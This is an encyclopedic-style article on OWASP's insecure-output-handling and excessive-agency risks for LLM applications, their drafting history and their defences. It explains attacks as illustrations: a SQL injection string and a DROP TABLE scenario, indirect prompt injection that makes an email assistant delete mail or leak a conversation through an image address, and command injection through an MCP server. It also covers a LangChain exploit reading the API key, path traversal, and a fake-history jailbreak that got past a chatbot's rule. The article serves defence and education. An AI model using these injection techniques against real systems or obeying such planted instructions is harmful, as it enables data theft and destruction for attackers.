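# Insecure Output Handling and Excessive Agency in the OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications

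## How a language-model application turns text into effects

Insecure output handling and excessive agency are two weaknesses in software that relies on large language models (LLMs), the programs that generate replies in chatbots such as ChatGPT. Insecure output handling is the failure to check or convert a model's text before other software uses it. Excessive agency is the failure to limit the actions that text can trigger, so that an unexpected or manipulated output can cause damage. Both names come from the Top 10 for LLM Applications, a ranked list of security risks that the software security foundation OWASP has published since 2023. In the 2025 edition, OWASP renamed the first risk "improper output handling".

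### OWASP and its Top 10 lists

OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, is a non-profit that began in December 2001 and incorporated in the United States in 2004. It gives away everything it produces, including code, documentation and standards. Its best-known publication is a Top 10 list of web application risks, first published in 2003. The language-model list uses the same format.

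According to Infosecurity Magazine's *What the OWASP Top 10 for LLMs Means for the Future*, Steve Wilson, then chief product officer at Contrast Security, wrote version 0.1 alone over a weekend in spring 2023 because no comprehensive resource on these models' vulnerabilities existed. OWASP approved the project that May. By version 1.1 in October, OWASP (2023) counted a team of nearly 500 experts, with more than 125 active contributors. Team members had written up 43 distinct threats and cut them to ten in several rounds of voting. Smaller groups then worked on each of the ten and put it out for public review. The early lists therefore reflect what experts judged important rather than how often each problem occurs. OWASP brought incident records into the ranking only in 2026.

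Each of the ten risks is an "entry" labelled with a number and a year, so LLM05:2025 is the fifth entry of the 2025 edition. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* follows the usual layout. It starts with a description that defines the weakness and distinguishes it from related risks, then lists common examples, a line each, and seven preventive measures. Short attack scenarios come next. In one, a user of a chat feature for querying a database asks to delete every table, and the application runs the model's query without checking it. The entry ends with references to outside research.

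None of this is a test that an application can pass. OWASP calls its 2021 web-application Top 10 "primarily an awareness document" and, for anyone who wants to use it as a coding standard, "the bare minimum", because the list documents risks and many risks are hard to test for. Insecure design, one of the web entries, is beyond most forms of testing. Organisations that want something verifiable should use OWASP's Application Security Verification Standard instead. The same reasoning applies to the language-model list. OWASP gives that project much the same purpose, "identifying, documenting, and raising awareness" of risks, and no scanner can decide how much power an assistant needs for its job. Infosecurity Magazine calls the list the first industry standard for language models, which is too strong unless "standard" means only that many people consult it.

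### From request to effect

An email assistant might also be able to open web pages. When a user asks it to summarize a page, the application, which is ordinary code written by a developer, assembles a prompt. The prompt contains the developer's standing instructions (the "system prompt"), the user's request, the text of the page and a description of the functions available to the model. Many applications also include the earlier conversation or passages retrieved from a company's documents. The model receives all of this as one long input.

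The model then generates its reply piece by piece. Generating the text does not itself send a message, change a file, or have any other outside effect. Any such effect depends on what the application does with the text.

The application may display the model's output. In the example, the summary appears in the user's browser or chat window. This is often harmless, but browsers run some kinds of text as code and fetch any image whose address the text contains, so even displaying the output can have effects.

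The application may pass the model's text to an interpreter, which is software that treats the text it receives as instructions. Database engines, browsers and shells (programs that run operating-system commands) are all interpreters. For example, a reporting tool may send queries written by the model to a database engine. Because browsers are interpreters, displaying text in one can also involve interpreting it.

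The application may also treat the text as a request to call an extension, which is any function a model can call. Extensions are also called plugins, tools or skills. The model usually generates a small structured fragment, such as `{"function": "delete_email", "id": 4127}`. The email is deleted only when application code recognises the fragment, looks up the function and runs it with whatever credentials the application holds. The code then adds the result to the prompt so that the model can generate the next step. An application that repeats this loop with little human involvement between steps is an agent.

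The application's responsibility begins when the model finishes generating text. Conventional code does everything after that, and a developer can inspect it, restrict it, and make it refuse requests. OWASP's entry on output handling, LLM05:2025, covers outputs that have not had enough "validation, sanitization, and handling" before they go to other components. Validation means checking that the text has the expected form, and sanitization means removing or neutralising the dangerous parts. Some model providers run tools such as web search on their own servers. Conventional code still takes over when generation ends, but it belongs to the provider.

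### Injection in databases and in prompts

Trouble with text that reaches an interpreter is older than language models. Suppose a shop's website looks up orders in SQL, the language of most databases, and builds each query by pasting in whatever name the visitor types:

`SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = '[name]'`

A visitor who types `Ada` gets Ada's orders. A visitor who types `x' OR '1'='1` turns the query into this:

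`SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = 'x' OR '1'='1'`

The quotation mark after the x closes the name early, and the database treats the rest as part of the command. Since 1 always equals 1, the condition holds for every row, and the visitor receives everybody's orders. This attack is called SQL injection. The database worked correctly, but it received a single string with no indication of which characters came from the programmer and which from the visitor. The standard remedy is a parameterized query, in which the programmer sends the command with a blank in it and supplies the value separately, so that the database never parses the value as a command. OWASP recommends the same technique for every database operation that involves a model's output.

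Prompt injection is text that makes a model act against its developer's intent. It has a similar cause. According to version 1.1 of the OWASP list, language models do not separate instructions from external data, because both arrive as natural language. But the same remedy does not work here. OWASP advises developers to mark the web page as untrusted, but the mark is only more input, which the model may not follow. OWASP concluded in 2023 that there was "no fool-proof prevention within the LLM". In 2026 it took a firmer position, telling developers to assume that the model's instruction boundary will eventually fail and to constrain what the model may do and what its outputs may reach, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*.

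Direct prompt injection comes from the user, who might type an instruction to ignore the developer's rules and reveal private data. Indirect prompt injection comes from content the model reads, such as a web page, a file or an email. In one OWASP scenario, a résumé contains hidden instructions that lead a model to recommend the candidate regardless of what else the document says. In another, a web page instructs the model to insert an image whose address contains a summary of the user's conversation, and the browser sends that summary when it requests the image. The planted text can be invisible to people as long as the software parses it. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) adds that attackers can also hide instructions in images, audio or video, and describes that route as mostly undefended.

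### The confused deputy

One of OWASP's 2023 scenarios closely matches the email assistant. An attacker puts instructions on a web page for the model to ignore the user and delete the user's emails. When the user asks for a summary of the page, the model generates a deletion request instead of a summary, or along with one, and the application carries out the deletion.

The attacker in this example has no access to the mailbox, but the assistant does. OWASP describes models under indirect injection as "confused deputies", an older computer security term for programs tricked into using their own authority on someone else's behalf. The attack passes a conventional access check because the mail server receives a request from an authorised application acting for an authorised user, and the request contains no sign that a stranger's web page prompted it.

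Least privilege, a principle from general security engineering, limits the harm by giving each component only the access its task needs. A summarising assistant needs to read web pages and perhaps mail, but it does not need to delete anything. If its credentials do not permit deletion, an attacker's text cannot make it delete anything. OWASP recommends enforcing this by issuing the model its own access tokens, with permissions set for each function.

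Complete mediation means checking every request against policy in the system that carries it out. For the mailbox, the mail server checks each deletion request as it arrives and decides whether to allow it. A line in the system prompt forbidding deletion can't replace this check, because it relies on the same model that the attacker's text may be steering. OWASP (2023) took this view from its first draft, version 0.5, stating that models "should not self-police" and that controls belong in the APIs, the interfaces through which programs call one another. Wilson gave similar advice in 2026, which Constantin (2026) summarises in *The hardest AI security problems now live in what an agent is* as read-only tools, requests that run under the user's own limited identity, and a point between the model and all downstream systems that enforces policy. That enforcement point provides complete mediation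 only if every request to the mail server passes through it.

Even together, these principles do not fully solve the email case. Suppose the assistant legitimately has a deletion function because its job includes tidying the mailbox, and it runs under the user's identity. The mail server checks a deletion request and allows it because users may delete their own mail. For this reason, OWASP also advises that the application get the user's approval before privileged operations such as sending or deleting email. It warns, however, that a compromised model may hide or alter information on its way to the user. A confirmation box that shows the actual request therefore protects the user much better than one that shows the model's account of what it is about to do.

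### Why the text is untrusted when the user is honest

OWASP's general rule is to treat the model "as any other user", with a zero-trust approach in which no request is trusted simply because of where it came from. The email case, in which the user typed nothing wrong, shows why this matters even for an internal tool used only by well-meaning employees. An application can verify who is at the keyboard and still not know who shaped the model's text, since anyone who can write to a page, document or inbox that the model reads can influence it. LLM05:2025 describes the result as similar to giving users "indirect access to additional functionality", though with indirect injection the people who gain that access need not be users.

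Models also make mistakes when no attacker is present. The assistant might respond to an ordinary instruction by generating a deletion request with the wrong message number. OWASP gives the example of a coding assistant that recommends a software package that does not exist. An attacker can then publish malware under the invented name, and a developer may download it. In a passage that Invicti quotes from the 2026 edition, OWASP says that when confident output drives a tool call, "a wrong answer turns into a wrong action". Filters that look for attacks offer little protection against such mistakes because there may be no attack to find, but restrictions on what the output can reach work whether or not there is an attacker.

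How far to take this distrust is less clear. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre's *Artificial intelligence insecure output handling* advises developers never to execute model output automatically, and to keep it out of shells and privileged functions. That is sound advice for a chatbot, but developers who followed it literally could build few useful agents, since agents are meant to act on model output automatically. The centre also advises applying least privilege so that a failure does less damage, which is less restrictive and suits more applications. OWASP (2026) quoted Wilson making a similar point when it announced the 2026 edition. He said that security must assume that AI "will sometimes fail or be fooled", and put enforceable controls around what these systems can access, decide and do.

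### Editions of the list

The year in the name of a later OWASP edition may not be the year it was published, and OWASP's pages sometimes give publication dates that are a day or two apart.

- Version 0.5, 1 July 2023. A draft, which OWASP called a "preview".
- Version 1.0, 1 August 2023. This is the date OWASP (2023) printed on the document; Paganini (2023), in *OWASP Top 10 for LLM (Large Language Model) applications is out!*, reported the release on 3 August.
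- Version 1.1, 16 October 2023.
- 2025 edition, November 2024. The download page from OWASP (2024) bears the date 17 November, and the press release from OWASP (2024) the date 19 November.
- 2026 edition, August 2026. The download page from OWASP (2026) bears the date 3 August, while Infosecurity Magazine gives 4 August. The cover image also showed 4 August at first, according to Eric (2026), in *OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications 全覽*, but by 12 August OWASP had changed the publication date in the document to "to be determined".

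## How the 2023 drafts separated output and action from prompt injection

The first draft of the list had no entries on output handling or excessive agency. OWASP added both in version 0.5 and revised them over the next three versions, all within five months of announcing the project. During that time, it switched from organising this part of the list by what an attacker could achieve to organising it by which control a developer had left out. OWASP gave reasons for only a few of these changes, so the reasons for the rest have to be inferred from the wording of successive versions.

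### The May 2023 draft

Wilson produced the first list largely with ChatGPT. In O'Reilly's *The OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications*, a chapter of his book on language-model security, he describes collecting research papers and blog posts in spring 2023 and using ChatGPT to summarize them. He then gave it a few examples from the web-application Top 10 and asked it to draft a list for language models in a similar format. He sent the result to Jeff Williams, a founder of OWASP and the author of its original Top 10, without telling him that it was "primarily machine generated". Williams encouraged him to continue. But in The Application Security Podcast's *Steve Wilson -- OWASP Top Ten for LLMs*, recorded a week or two after the project began, Wilson said he had written the list "just for fun" after a good deal of research and had been embarrassed to send it, and he didn't mention ChatGPT's part.

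OWASP (2023) announced the project on 23 May. Wilson's announcement justified a separate list on the grounds that applications built on language models have requirements of their own, different from those of standard web apps. Much of his draft could nevertheless have come from a web list. ReversingLabs, a software security company, printed the ten entries in June:

1. Prompt injections
2. Data leakage
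3. Inadequate sandboxing
4. Unauthorized code execution
5. SSRF (server-side request forgery) vulnerabilities
6. Overreliance on LLM-generated content
7. Inadequate AI alignment
8. Insufficient access controls
9. Improper error handling
10. Training data poisoning

ReversingLabs pointed out that data leakage, request forgery and access control resembled entries in OWASP's lists for web applications and APIs. The resemblance would be unsurprising if ChatGPT used the web list as a template, though Wilson has not made this connection himself.

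Most of what later fell under Insecure Output Handling and Excessive Agency appears in four of these entries: inadequate sandboxing, unauthorized code execution, server-side request forgery and insufficient access controls.

Server-side request forgery is an older web attack that makes a server fetch an address the attacker chooses. Suppose a website previews other pages. A visitor submits an address, and the site's server fetches the page and displays part of it. An outsider cannot open the company's internal payroll system, but the server may be able to because it is inside the company's network. If the outsider submits the payroll system's address, the server may fetch the page and display it. GCVE's *Server-Side Request Forgery (SSRF)* reproduces the standard definition from the Common Weakness Enumeration, a public catalogue of software flaws. The flaw is that the server does not sufficiently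 ensure "that the request is being sent to the expected destination".

When an application includes a language model, the model's text may supply the address. On The Application Security Podcast, Wilson gave the example of a user who asks a model connected to a company's databases to find other databases on the network and bring back the useful information. PortSwigger's *Web LLM attacks* compares attacks on language-model integrations in general to request forgery, because the attacker uses the model to reach data and APIs they couldn't otherwise access. The server in the payroll example is a confused deputy in the same sense as the email assistant that deletes its user's mail.

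The other entries overlapped with this one and with each other. Writing for the security company Vulcan, Divinsky (2023) went through the draft in *OWASP Top 10 LLM risks* while it was still open for changes. A sandbox limits what the software inside it can reach, and inadequate sandboxing meant that the model was not isolated enough from sensitive systems. Unauthorized code execution meant that an attacker used prompts to run commands on the underlying machine. But Divinsky also lists poor sandboxing as a cause of both unauthorized code execution and request forgery. One of the two scenarios for inadequate sandboxing is an attacker who gets the model to execute unauthorized commands, which is unauthorized code execution. The recommended fixes are also nearly the same, with all three entries calling for isolation, restricted access, regular audits and logging.

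If Divinsky's summary is faithful, the draft also put its main check against code execution and request forgery in the wrong place, by having developers validate the user's prompt before the model received it. That doesn't stop instructions in a web page the model reads later, or a harmless prompt that happens to produce a dangerous command. Divinsky lists encoding the model's output under prompt injection and filtering it under data leakage, so a developer who consulted the entry on code execution would have found neither.

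ReversingLabs summarized the risk of insufficient access controls as unauthorized users interacting with a system. That description doesn't fit the email example, where the user is authorized to use the assistant and the problem is what the assistant can do on a stranger's instructions.

### Version 0.5

Wilson had expected 10 or 15 people to take an interest. About 170 joined the kick-off call, and 260 had signed up by early June, when the group was working to an eight-week plan. Members brainstormed for a month, then voted on the resulting 43 proposals. (That count is OWASP's; Infosecurity Magazine reports over 45.) At least some proposals had individual authors. The supply-chain entry in version 0.5 links to one on "insecure plugin integration" by John Sotiropoulos, a security architect at the software company Kainos and a member of the project's core group.

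Wilson told ReversingLabs that one of the project's biggest challenges would be getting more than 200 experts from different disciplines to agree on one list. On the podcast, he said that members were arguing about what counts as a vulnerability in this field, since some entries in his draft involved more human factors than OWASP lists usually do.

Version 0.5 came out on 1 July, when the group had more than 370 members. According to OWASP (2023), it kept and improved half of the entries in the "straw man" first draft and replaced the rest. Prompt injection, data leakage, overreliance and training data poisoning are easy to recognise among the entries it kept. The fifth is probably insufficient access controls, rewritten as Permission Issues. Version 0.5 dropped the entries on sandboxing, code execution and request forgery, but its advice on training data still refers readers to "LLM03:2023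 - Inadequate Sandboxing".

Insecure Output Handling entered the list in second place, behind prompt injection. OWASP defined it as "a type of prompt injection vulnerability" in which software "blindly accepts" a model's output and passes it to other functions. This could lead to request forgery or remote code execution, which means running the attacker's commands on someone else's machine. Wilson's original list had given each of these its own entry. It could also lead to cross-site scripting, in which an attacker's code runs in another person's browser. OWASP advised developers to validate the model's responses before passing them to backend functions, and to encode them before sending them to users' browsers. Both measures apply to the model's output, whereas the May draft had concentrated on its input.

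Because prompts can control what a model generates, OWASP had a reason to file poor output handling under prompt injection, as the last stage of an attack. But that reasoning covers only output that an attacker has shaped, not the model's own mistakes.

The Excessive Agency entry in the same version did not have this restriction. It covers undesirable operation of the model whatever the root cause, and its examples of causes include hallucination and innocent but badly written prompts as well as direct and indirect injection. The list therefore separated action from prompt injection from 1 July, but did not do the same for output handling until a month later.

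A scenario that OWASP included in version 0.5 but dropped from the next version shows the purpose of the new entry. A customer-service model can issue refunds through a payments system, and its system prompt limits refunds to one month's subscription fee. A malicious customer persuades the model to refund 100 years of fees. OWASP's remedy was to put the one-month limit into the refund API, so that the payments system would refuse the request whatever the model had generated. In the May draft, this case could have fallen under several entries, including prompt injection and inadequate AI alignment (which ReversingLabs described as a mismatch between a model's behaviour and its intended use), but neither label points developers to the refund API.

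Excessive Agency was one of three entries in version 0.5 about the power that applications give to models. Permission Issues covered applications that fail to track who authorized a request as it passes from one plugin to another. Insecure Plugins covered plugins that accept free-form text instead of separate, checked values. In one example, a weather plugin lets the model supply a whole web address, and an attacker replaces the weather service's address with one of their own.

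The three overlapped. Permission Issues and Excessive Agency both gave the example of an indirect injection that abuses an email account, to steal the contents of the inbox in the first and to send spam in the second. Both entries recommended that a person approve sensitive actions. Excessive Agency and Insecure Plugins both recommended least privilege. Trend Micro, another security company, sorted the ten risks into just three groups, one of them for "exploited privileges and unauthorized actions".

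### Version 0.9 and the end of Permission Issues

OWASP released version 0.9 in July as a "release candidate". By then the group had grown to more than 440 members, and a sub-team of at least 12 experts had examined each entry. In the introduction, OWASP reported that expert feedback had led it to merge two vulnerabilities from version 0.5 and add one that had narrowly missed inclusion before, but it did not name these vulnerabilities.

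Model Theft is the only entry on a new subject. Permission Issues is no longer an entry, but its three examples, both of its attack scenarios, and its rule that a plugin should run with the lowest authorization of any plugin that contributed to the prompt reappear almost word for word under Insecure Plugin Design, the new name for Insecure Plugins. The revised Excessive Agency entry also covers some of the same concern, advising developers to track each user's authorization and carry out actions under that user's identity.

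The table matches the entries by subject. The May column gives the nearest equivalents, since OWASP published no such mapping.

| Subject | May draft | Version 0.5 | Versions 0.9 to 1.1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model text that other software accepts unchecked | Unauthorized code execution; SSRF | LLM02 Insecure Output Handling | LLM02 Insecure Output Handling |
| Actions with more power than the task needs | Inadequate sandboxing | LLM08 Excessive Agency | LLM08 Excessive Agency |
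| Tools that accept free-form input | None | LLM10 Insecure Plugins | LLM07 Insecure Plugin Design |
| Authorization of requests | Insufficient access controls | LLM06 Permission Issues | Part of LLM07 |

Excessive Agency changed more than any other entry on this subject. In version 0.5, its only example of the vulnerability was a model that triggers undesirable actions, which restates the definition. Version 0.9 traced the weakness to excessive functionality, excessive permissions or excessive autonomy, and gave six concrete examples, such as a plugin for reading documents that can also delete them. Version 0.5 had also listed rate limiting, which caps the number of actions in a given period, as a preventive measure. Version 0.9 moved it to a separate group of measures that reduce the damage but do not prevent the weakness, since an assistant limited to ten emails an hour can still send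 ten unwanted ones.

The definition of Insecure Output Handling did not change. The full entry in version 0.9 still called it a type of prompt injection, although the same version added a scenario in which a user asks a database chat feature to delete every table. Prompt injection is a poor description of that case because the user makes a plain request and the model writes the query as designed.

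### Versions 1.0 and 1.1

The phrase disappeared in version 1.0, on 1 August. The slides for that version describe output handling as a vulnerability that arises when "a downstream component blindly accepts" a model's output. OWASP did not explain the change. The simplest explanation is that the old definition did not fit the entry's own examples, and that Excessive Agency already had a definition that did not depend on the cause.

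Version 1.1, released on 16 October, defined insecure output handling more precisely as insufficient validation, sanitization and handling of outputs before they go to other components. The 2025 edition kept this definition. OWASP also listed several conditions that make the consequences worse, including the application's vulnerability to indirect prompt injection. In July, output handling had been part of the prompt injection category.

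The new definition also changed which component is at fault. Under the earlier wording, the fault lies with the component that "blindly accepts" the text, and a plugin that accepts unchecked text from a model fits that description as well as it fits Insecure Plugin Design. In version 1.1, the failure happens before the text reaches the next component, so the application that sends it is at fault. A third-party plugin that does not validate its inputs became another of the aggravating conditions. Insecure Output Handling therefore covers checking the text as it leaves, and Insecure Plugin Design covers checking it as it arrives. OWASP had already argued for both checks in version 0.9, where it warned plugin developers not to rely on output sanitization because it may be impossible in a chain of plugins, or someone may have omitted it.

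OWASP did not say that this was why it rewrote the definition. Version 1.1 explicitly distinguished Insecure Output Handling only from Overreliance, the entry on trusting a model's accuracy too much. Insecure Output Handling concerns what happens to text before it reaches other software, while Overreliance concerns whether people and systems should depend on the content. Either problem can occur without the other. For example, an accurate answer can still contain characters that a browser runs as code.

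The slides that OWASP (2023) issued for version 1.1 kept the "blindly accepts" definition from version 1.0, so their definition of the entry differs slightly from the one in the full document.

### What changed when the entries named missing controls

Unauthorized code execution and server-side request forgery describe what an attacker has managed to do, and many different mistakes can lead to either. Insecure output handling describes something the developer did not do at a particular point in the program. Inadequate sandboxing and insufficient access controls were already closer to this kind of entry, but neither specified which request to check or where.

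OWASP came closest to giving a general reason in version 1.1, where it wrote that the list does not "simply reiterate" vulnerabilities from its other Top 10 lists but examines what is distinctive about them in language-model applications. By that standard, a separate entry for request forgery was hard to justify, because the attack is the same as on any website except that a model's text can now trigger it. But OWASP published this statement months after dropping the entry, so it may not have been the original reason.

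In practice, developers can look for the places in their code where model text passes to a shell, a database or a browser, and put a check at each one. A single check can prevent several outcomes. For example, a database tool that accepts only read queries on one table blocks deletions whether they are malicious or accidental. The entry also does not need rewriting whenever someone connects a model to a new kind of software. Different destinations still need different checks, because text that is safe in one can be dangerous in another, and even the short advice in version 0.5 had one rule for backend functions and another for browsers.

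Excessive Agency gained in a similar way, although Wilson's public defence of it was rather weak. Infosecurity Magazine wrote that Excessive Agency and Overreliance can sound more like psychological biases than technical vulnerabilities, and Wilson replied that such threats become relevant because language models are based on human language. That is a reasonable defence of Overreliance, but Excessive Agency hardly needs it, since from version 0.9 onwards the entry was about the functions, access rights and approvals that developers attach to a model, all of which are familiar in ordinary software.

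The drawback is that an attack no longer has one obvious place in the list, because an attack with one main outcome can depend on several missing controls. Security Innovation's *Exploring the Power and Potential Risks of Large Language Models (LLMs)* matched a set of threats to the 2023 entries and put cross-site scripting under both Prompt Injection and Insecure Output Handling. It put request forgery under Insecure Plugin Design alone, even though OWASP names it as a result of insecure output handling.

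OWASP's own examples are also hard to assign to a single entry. In one scenario under output handling in version 1.1, a general-purpose chatbot passes its response unchecked to a plugin, and the plugin shuts down for maintenance. The plugin has administrative functions that only a different, more privileged model was supposed to use. Checking the chatbot's output would have prevented the shutdown. So would removing the administrative functions from the plugin the chatbot uses, which is the remedy for excessive functionality, or having the plugin verify which model was calling it.

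## Model output run as commands, database queries or file paths

LLM05:2025, Improper Output Handling, still defines the failure as insufficient validation, sanitization and handling of a model's output before other software receives it. According to OWASP, this can lead to cross-site scripting in a browser, or to cross-site request forgery, in which a malicious page makes a logged-in user's browser send a request the user never intended. On a server, it can lead to server-side request forgery, remote code execution or privilege escalation, in which an attacker gains rights nobody granted them.

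Most of these attacks are old, apart from the model's involvement. MITRE's *CWE-1426*, an entry on generative AI output in the Common Weakness Enumeration, compares many of them to second-order SQL injection, in which an application stores hostile text and later pastes it into a query. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026) examined eight classic web attacks in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* and similarly concluded that the model usually carries an attacker's influence to a weak component rather than creating the weakness. Developers' existing checks for each component therefore mostly still apply, but some rely on a programmer having written the command, which may not be true once a model is involved.

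### What the 2025 edition added

OWASP expanded most of the entry for the 2025 edition. The two common examples in version 1.1 were output that goes straight into a shell or a similar function and output that a browser runs as code. The 2025 edition added examples with SQL queries, file paths and email templates, and raised the number of preventive measures from three to seven. The four new measures are context-aware encoding, parameterized queries, logging and monitoring, and a strict Content Security Policy, which limits the scripts a browser will run on a page.

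Context-aware encoding means rewriting text so that a particular interpreter treats it as data. Version 1.1 only told developers to encode output returned to users. The newer advice covers every destination, because the dangerous characters differ between destinations. A less-than sign can open a tag in a web page but is an ordinary character inside a quoted SQL value. A quotation mark can end that SQL value but is usually harmless in a paragraph on a web page. Encoding only helps when the output is supposed to be data. If an application is meant to run the output as a query or a program, encoding would stop it from working.

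Monitoring is an odd addition to a list of preventive measures because it mostly reveals attacks already under way. In version 1.1, OWASP recommended periodic manual monitoring under Prompt Injection but described it as "not a mitigation".

The 2026 edition still has an entry on improper output handling, according to SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications*.

### Shell commands

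A shell splits a line of text into a program name and arguments, and certain characters end one command and begin another. If an application builds the line by adding a model's text to a fixed command, that text can include a second command, which the shell will run with the application's permissions.

Snyk Labs, a security company's research group, demonstrated this in 2025 with a server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting models to outside tools. According to Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, the server offered a tool for running Amazon's cloud command-line program, and the tool would also run a second command added after the first. Such servers often run on a developer's own machine, where an outsider cannot reach them directly, but an attacker can leave an instruction in a file in a shared code repository. When the developer adds that file to a coding assistant's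 context and asks for something ordinary, such as a list of storage folders, the model includes the attacker's command in its tool request. The damage depends on what the server can access, which may include the developer's cloud account.

The best remedy is to avoid the shell. An operating system can start a program directly from a name and a list of separate arguments. When it does, no character in an argument can begin a new command. The developer fixes the program name, and the model supplies only the arguments. The application should still check the arguments against a list of permitted values, because many programs have options that overwrite files or start other programs.

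### Database queries

Parameterized queries keep the same separation of command and value when a developer has written the query. An assistant that looks up orders might use this one:

`SELECT status FROM orders WHERE customer_id = ? AND order_id = ?`

The application fills the first blank from the login session, and the model supplies the order number for the second.

Many applications have the model write the whole statement instead, because users ask questions that no developer foresaw. The application then has no developer-written statement to bind values to. It could ask the model for a statement with placeholders and a separate list of values, but the model would still have written the rest of the command.

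In OWASP's database scenario, a user asks to delete every table and the model generates a series of `DROP TABLE` commands. The parameterized queries that OWASP recommends would not prevent the deletion, because the commands contain no values that the application could send separately. Escaping would not help either, because the commands are valid SQL that does what the user asked, and nothing in them breaks out of quotation marks. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian consider parameterized queries necessary for values that users control, but insufficient when the model generates the structure of the query.

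The application therefore has to check what kind of statement the model has written. It can parse the text and run it only if it is a single `SELECT` on permitted tables. An allowlist like this is safer than a list of forbidden commands, which would have to cover all of the many ways SQL can change data. Checking only the first word is not enough, because in the PostgreSQL database a statement that ends in a `SELECT` can delete rows in an earlier clause, and a plain `SELECT` can call a function that changes data.

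Since a parser can miss such cases, the application should also connect through a read-only database account. The database engine then rejects a deletion even if the application's check let it through. The allowlist is still needed because it can also limit which functions a query calls and how many statements a request contains.

In *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks*, Pedro, Carreira and colleagues (2023) tested what happens without either check. They built a job-listing site with a chatbot that had full access to the database. The chatbot used GPT-3.5 and LangChain, a popular framework for applications built on language models. With LangChain's standard prompt, the chatbot ran any query a user requested. The researchers then added a rule against changing data. A simple request to ignore the rule failed, but a longer message with a fake record of an earlier, successful deletion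 worked in all 30 attempts. A rule against reading other people's records failed when the user claimed to be someone else.

Attackers could also change the database without using the chatbot themselves. In one test, the researchers planted instructions in a job description. When another user asked about job openings, the model read the description, changed a third person's email address in the database and then answered the question without mentioning the change. This attack needed a version of the chatbot that could run several queries for one question.

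The researchers then tried four defences on a bookshop application, again with GPT-3.5. The table groups their results by the kind of harm.

| Defence | Unwanted changes to data | Reading other users' data | Planted text that falsifies an answer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read-only database account | Stopped | Not stopped | Not stopped |
| Rewriting the model's query | Not stopped | Stopped | Not stopped |
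| Putting the user's own data in the prompt beforehand | Not stopped | Stopped | Not stopped |
| Second model that inspects query results | Stopped only when the attack came from planted text | Not stopped | Stopped |

The second row fills the largest gap left by a read-only account, which still allows a query for everyone's email address. Code in the application replaces each sensitive table in the model's query with a smaller one that contains only the current user's rows. For user 7, a request for all email addresses becomes:

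`SELECT email FROM (SELECT * FROM users WHERE id = 7) AS own_rows`

The model can still write a query for all the addresses, but the database returns only one. Rewriting the query took less than two milliseconds on average. PostgreSQL, the database Pedro and colleagues used, also supports rules for individual rows. Such rules could restrict the results in the same way inside the database, provided that the application reliably identifies the user to it. Pedro and colleagues proposed rewriting partly because, they wrote, database permissions apply only to whole tables, which overstates PostgreSQL's limits.

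The second model took about 0.4 seconds per check and is the weakest of the four defences, since hostile text can mislead it too. However, it was the only defence in the table that stopped falsified answers. A poisoned job description can make a chatbot report that there are no jobs, even when the query was correct and the account had read-only access, because the text misleads the model when it reads the query results.

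### Generated code

Some applications run code that the model writes. In Python, `eval` evaluates text as an expression, and `exec` runs it as a program. This code has the same access as the application, including its files, network connections and passwords.

The flaw that OWASP has cited for this risk since 2023 was in LLMMathChain, a LangChain component that answered mathematical questions by passing code from a model to `exec` and `eval`. Snyk's *Arbitrary Code Execution Affecting langchain package, versions [,0.0.142)* (2023), published on 5 April, demonstrated the flaw with a user asking the component to load Python's operating-system library and read the application's secret OpenAI key. INCIBE's *CVE-2023-29374* (2023) gives the flaw a severity of 9.8 out of 10. MITRE's *CVE-2023-29374* (2023) lists the affected versions as those up to 0.0.131, while Snyk includes everything before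 0.0.142 and advises upgrading to that version.

LangChain later had another code-execution flaw, this time through numexpr, a library for evaluating numerical expressions. According to GitLab's *Langchain vulnerable to arbitrary code execution via the evaluate function*, the flaw affected version 0.0.245, and the developers patched it in version 0.0.308. A function that evaluates formulas is still an interpreter and may accept more than formulas, so it may be less safe than it sounds.

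Developers can't solve this by checking each program before running it, because no checker can determine for every program whether it is safe. Suppose a checker could always determine whether a program will delete a file. Someone could take any calculation that deletes nothing and add a final line that deletes a file. The new program deletes the file only if the calculation finishes, so the checker's answer would also show whether the calculation finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no general procedure can determine this.

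A checker that rejects everything it cannot prove safe is practical for a tiny language, such as arithmetic with only numbers and four operators, but in Python it would reject many useful programs. Looser filters miss attacks. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe an agent that passed a model's reply to Jinja, a Python tool that fills in text templates and evaluates any expressions they contain. The attack started from an empty piece of text and worked through Python's internal objects until it reached a function for running operating-system commands. A filter that looked only for obvious commands at the start would have missed it. The developer could have prevented this attack by writing a fixed template and inserting the reply as a value, much as in a parameterized query.

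When the application needs to run the model's program, isolation has to be the main protection. The application runs the code in a separate container or virtual machine with no passwords, no network connection and only the files the task needs. It also limits the code's running time and memory, and deletes the environment afterwards. MITRE says that since the output cannot be trusted, developers should ensure that it operates in "an untrusted or non-privileged space".

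*Generative AI Models* (2024) gives an example similar to the LangChain calculator, in which an attacker gets the model to write code that encrypts a connected database or returns its contents. Both attacks depend on a database connection, which a calculator does not need. The code would fail in an isolated environment without that connection, even if nobody recognised it as malicious.

OWASP's seven preventive measures do not include isolation, even though `exec` and `eval` appear in the entry's first example. This is a significant omission, particularly because Wilson's first draft had an entry on sandboxing.

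Isolation protects what is outside the environment, but the program can still return a wrong answer, or text that contains further instructions for the model. The application therefore has to treat the result as untrusted. If the program has to update a company database, the developer must give it some access, and the checks on queries and accounts become necessary again.

### File paths and web addresses

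A model may supply only the name of a file, for example when a user asks an assistant to open last month's report. The application adds the name to the path of its reports folder and opens the file at that location. Two dots in a path mean the folder one level up, so a name with enough of these pairs can lead out of the reports folder to configuration files or passwords. This attack, called path traversal, can also overwrite the application's own code if the application writes files as well as reading them.

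To prevent path traversal, the application should convert the path to its final form, following any links to other folders, before checking that the file is inside the permitted folder. An even simpler method is to let the model choose from a list of document numbers and keep the real paths in the application. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) cites research by Shen and colleagues that found path traversal, SQL injection, command injection and code injection in agents.

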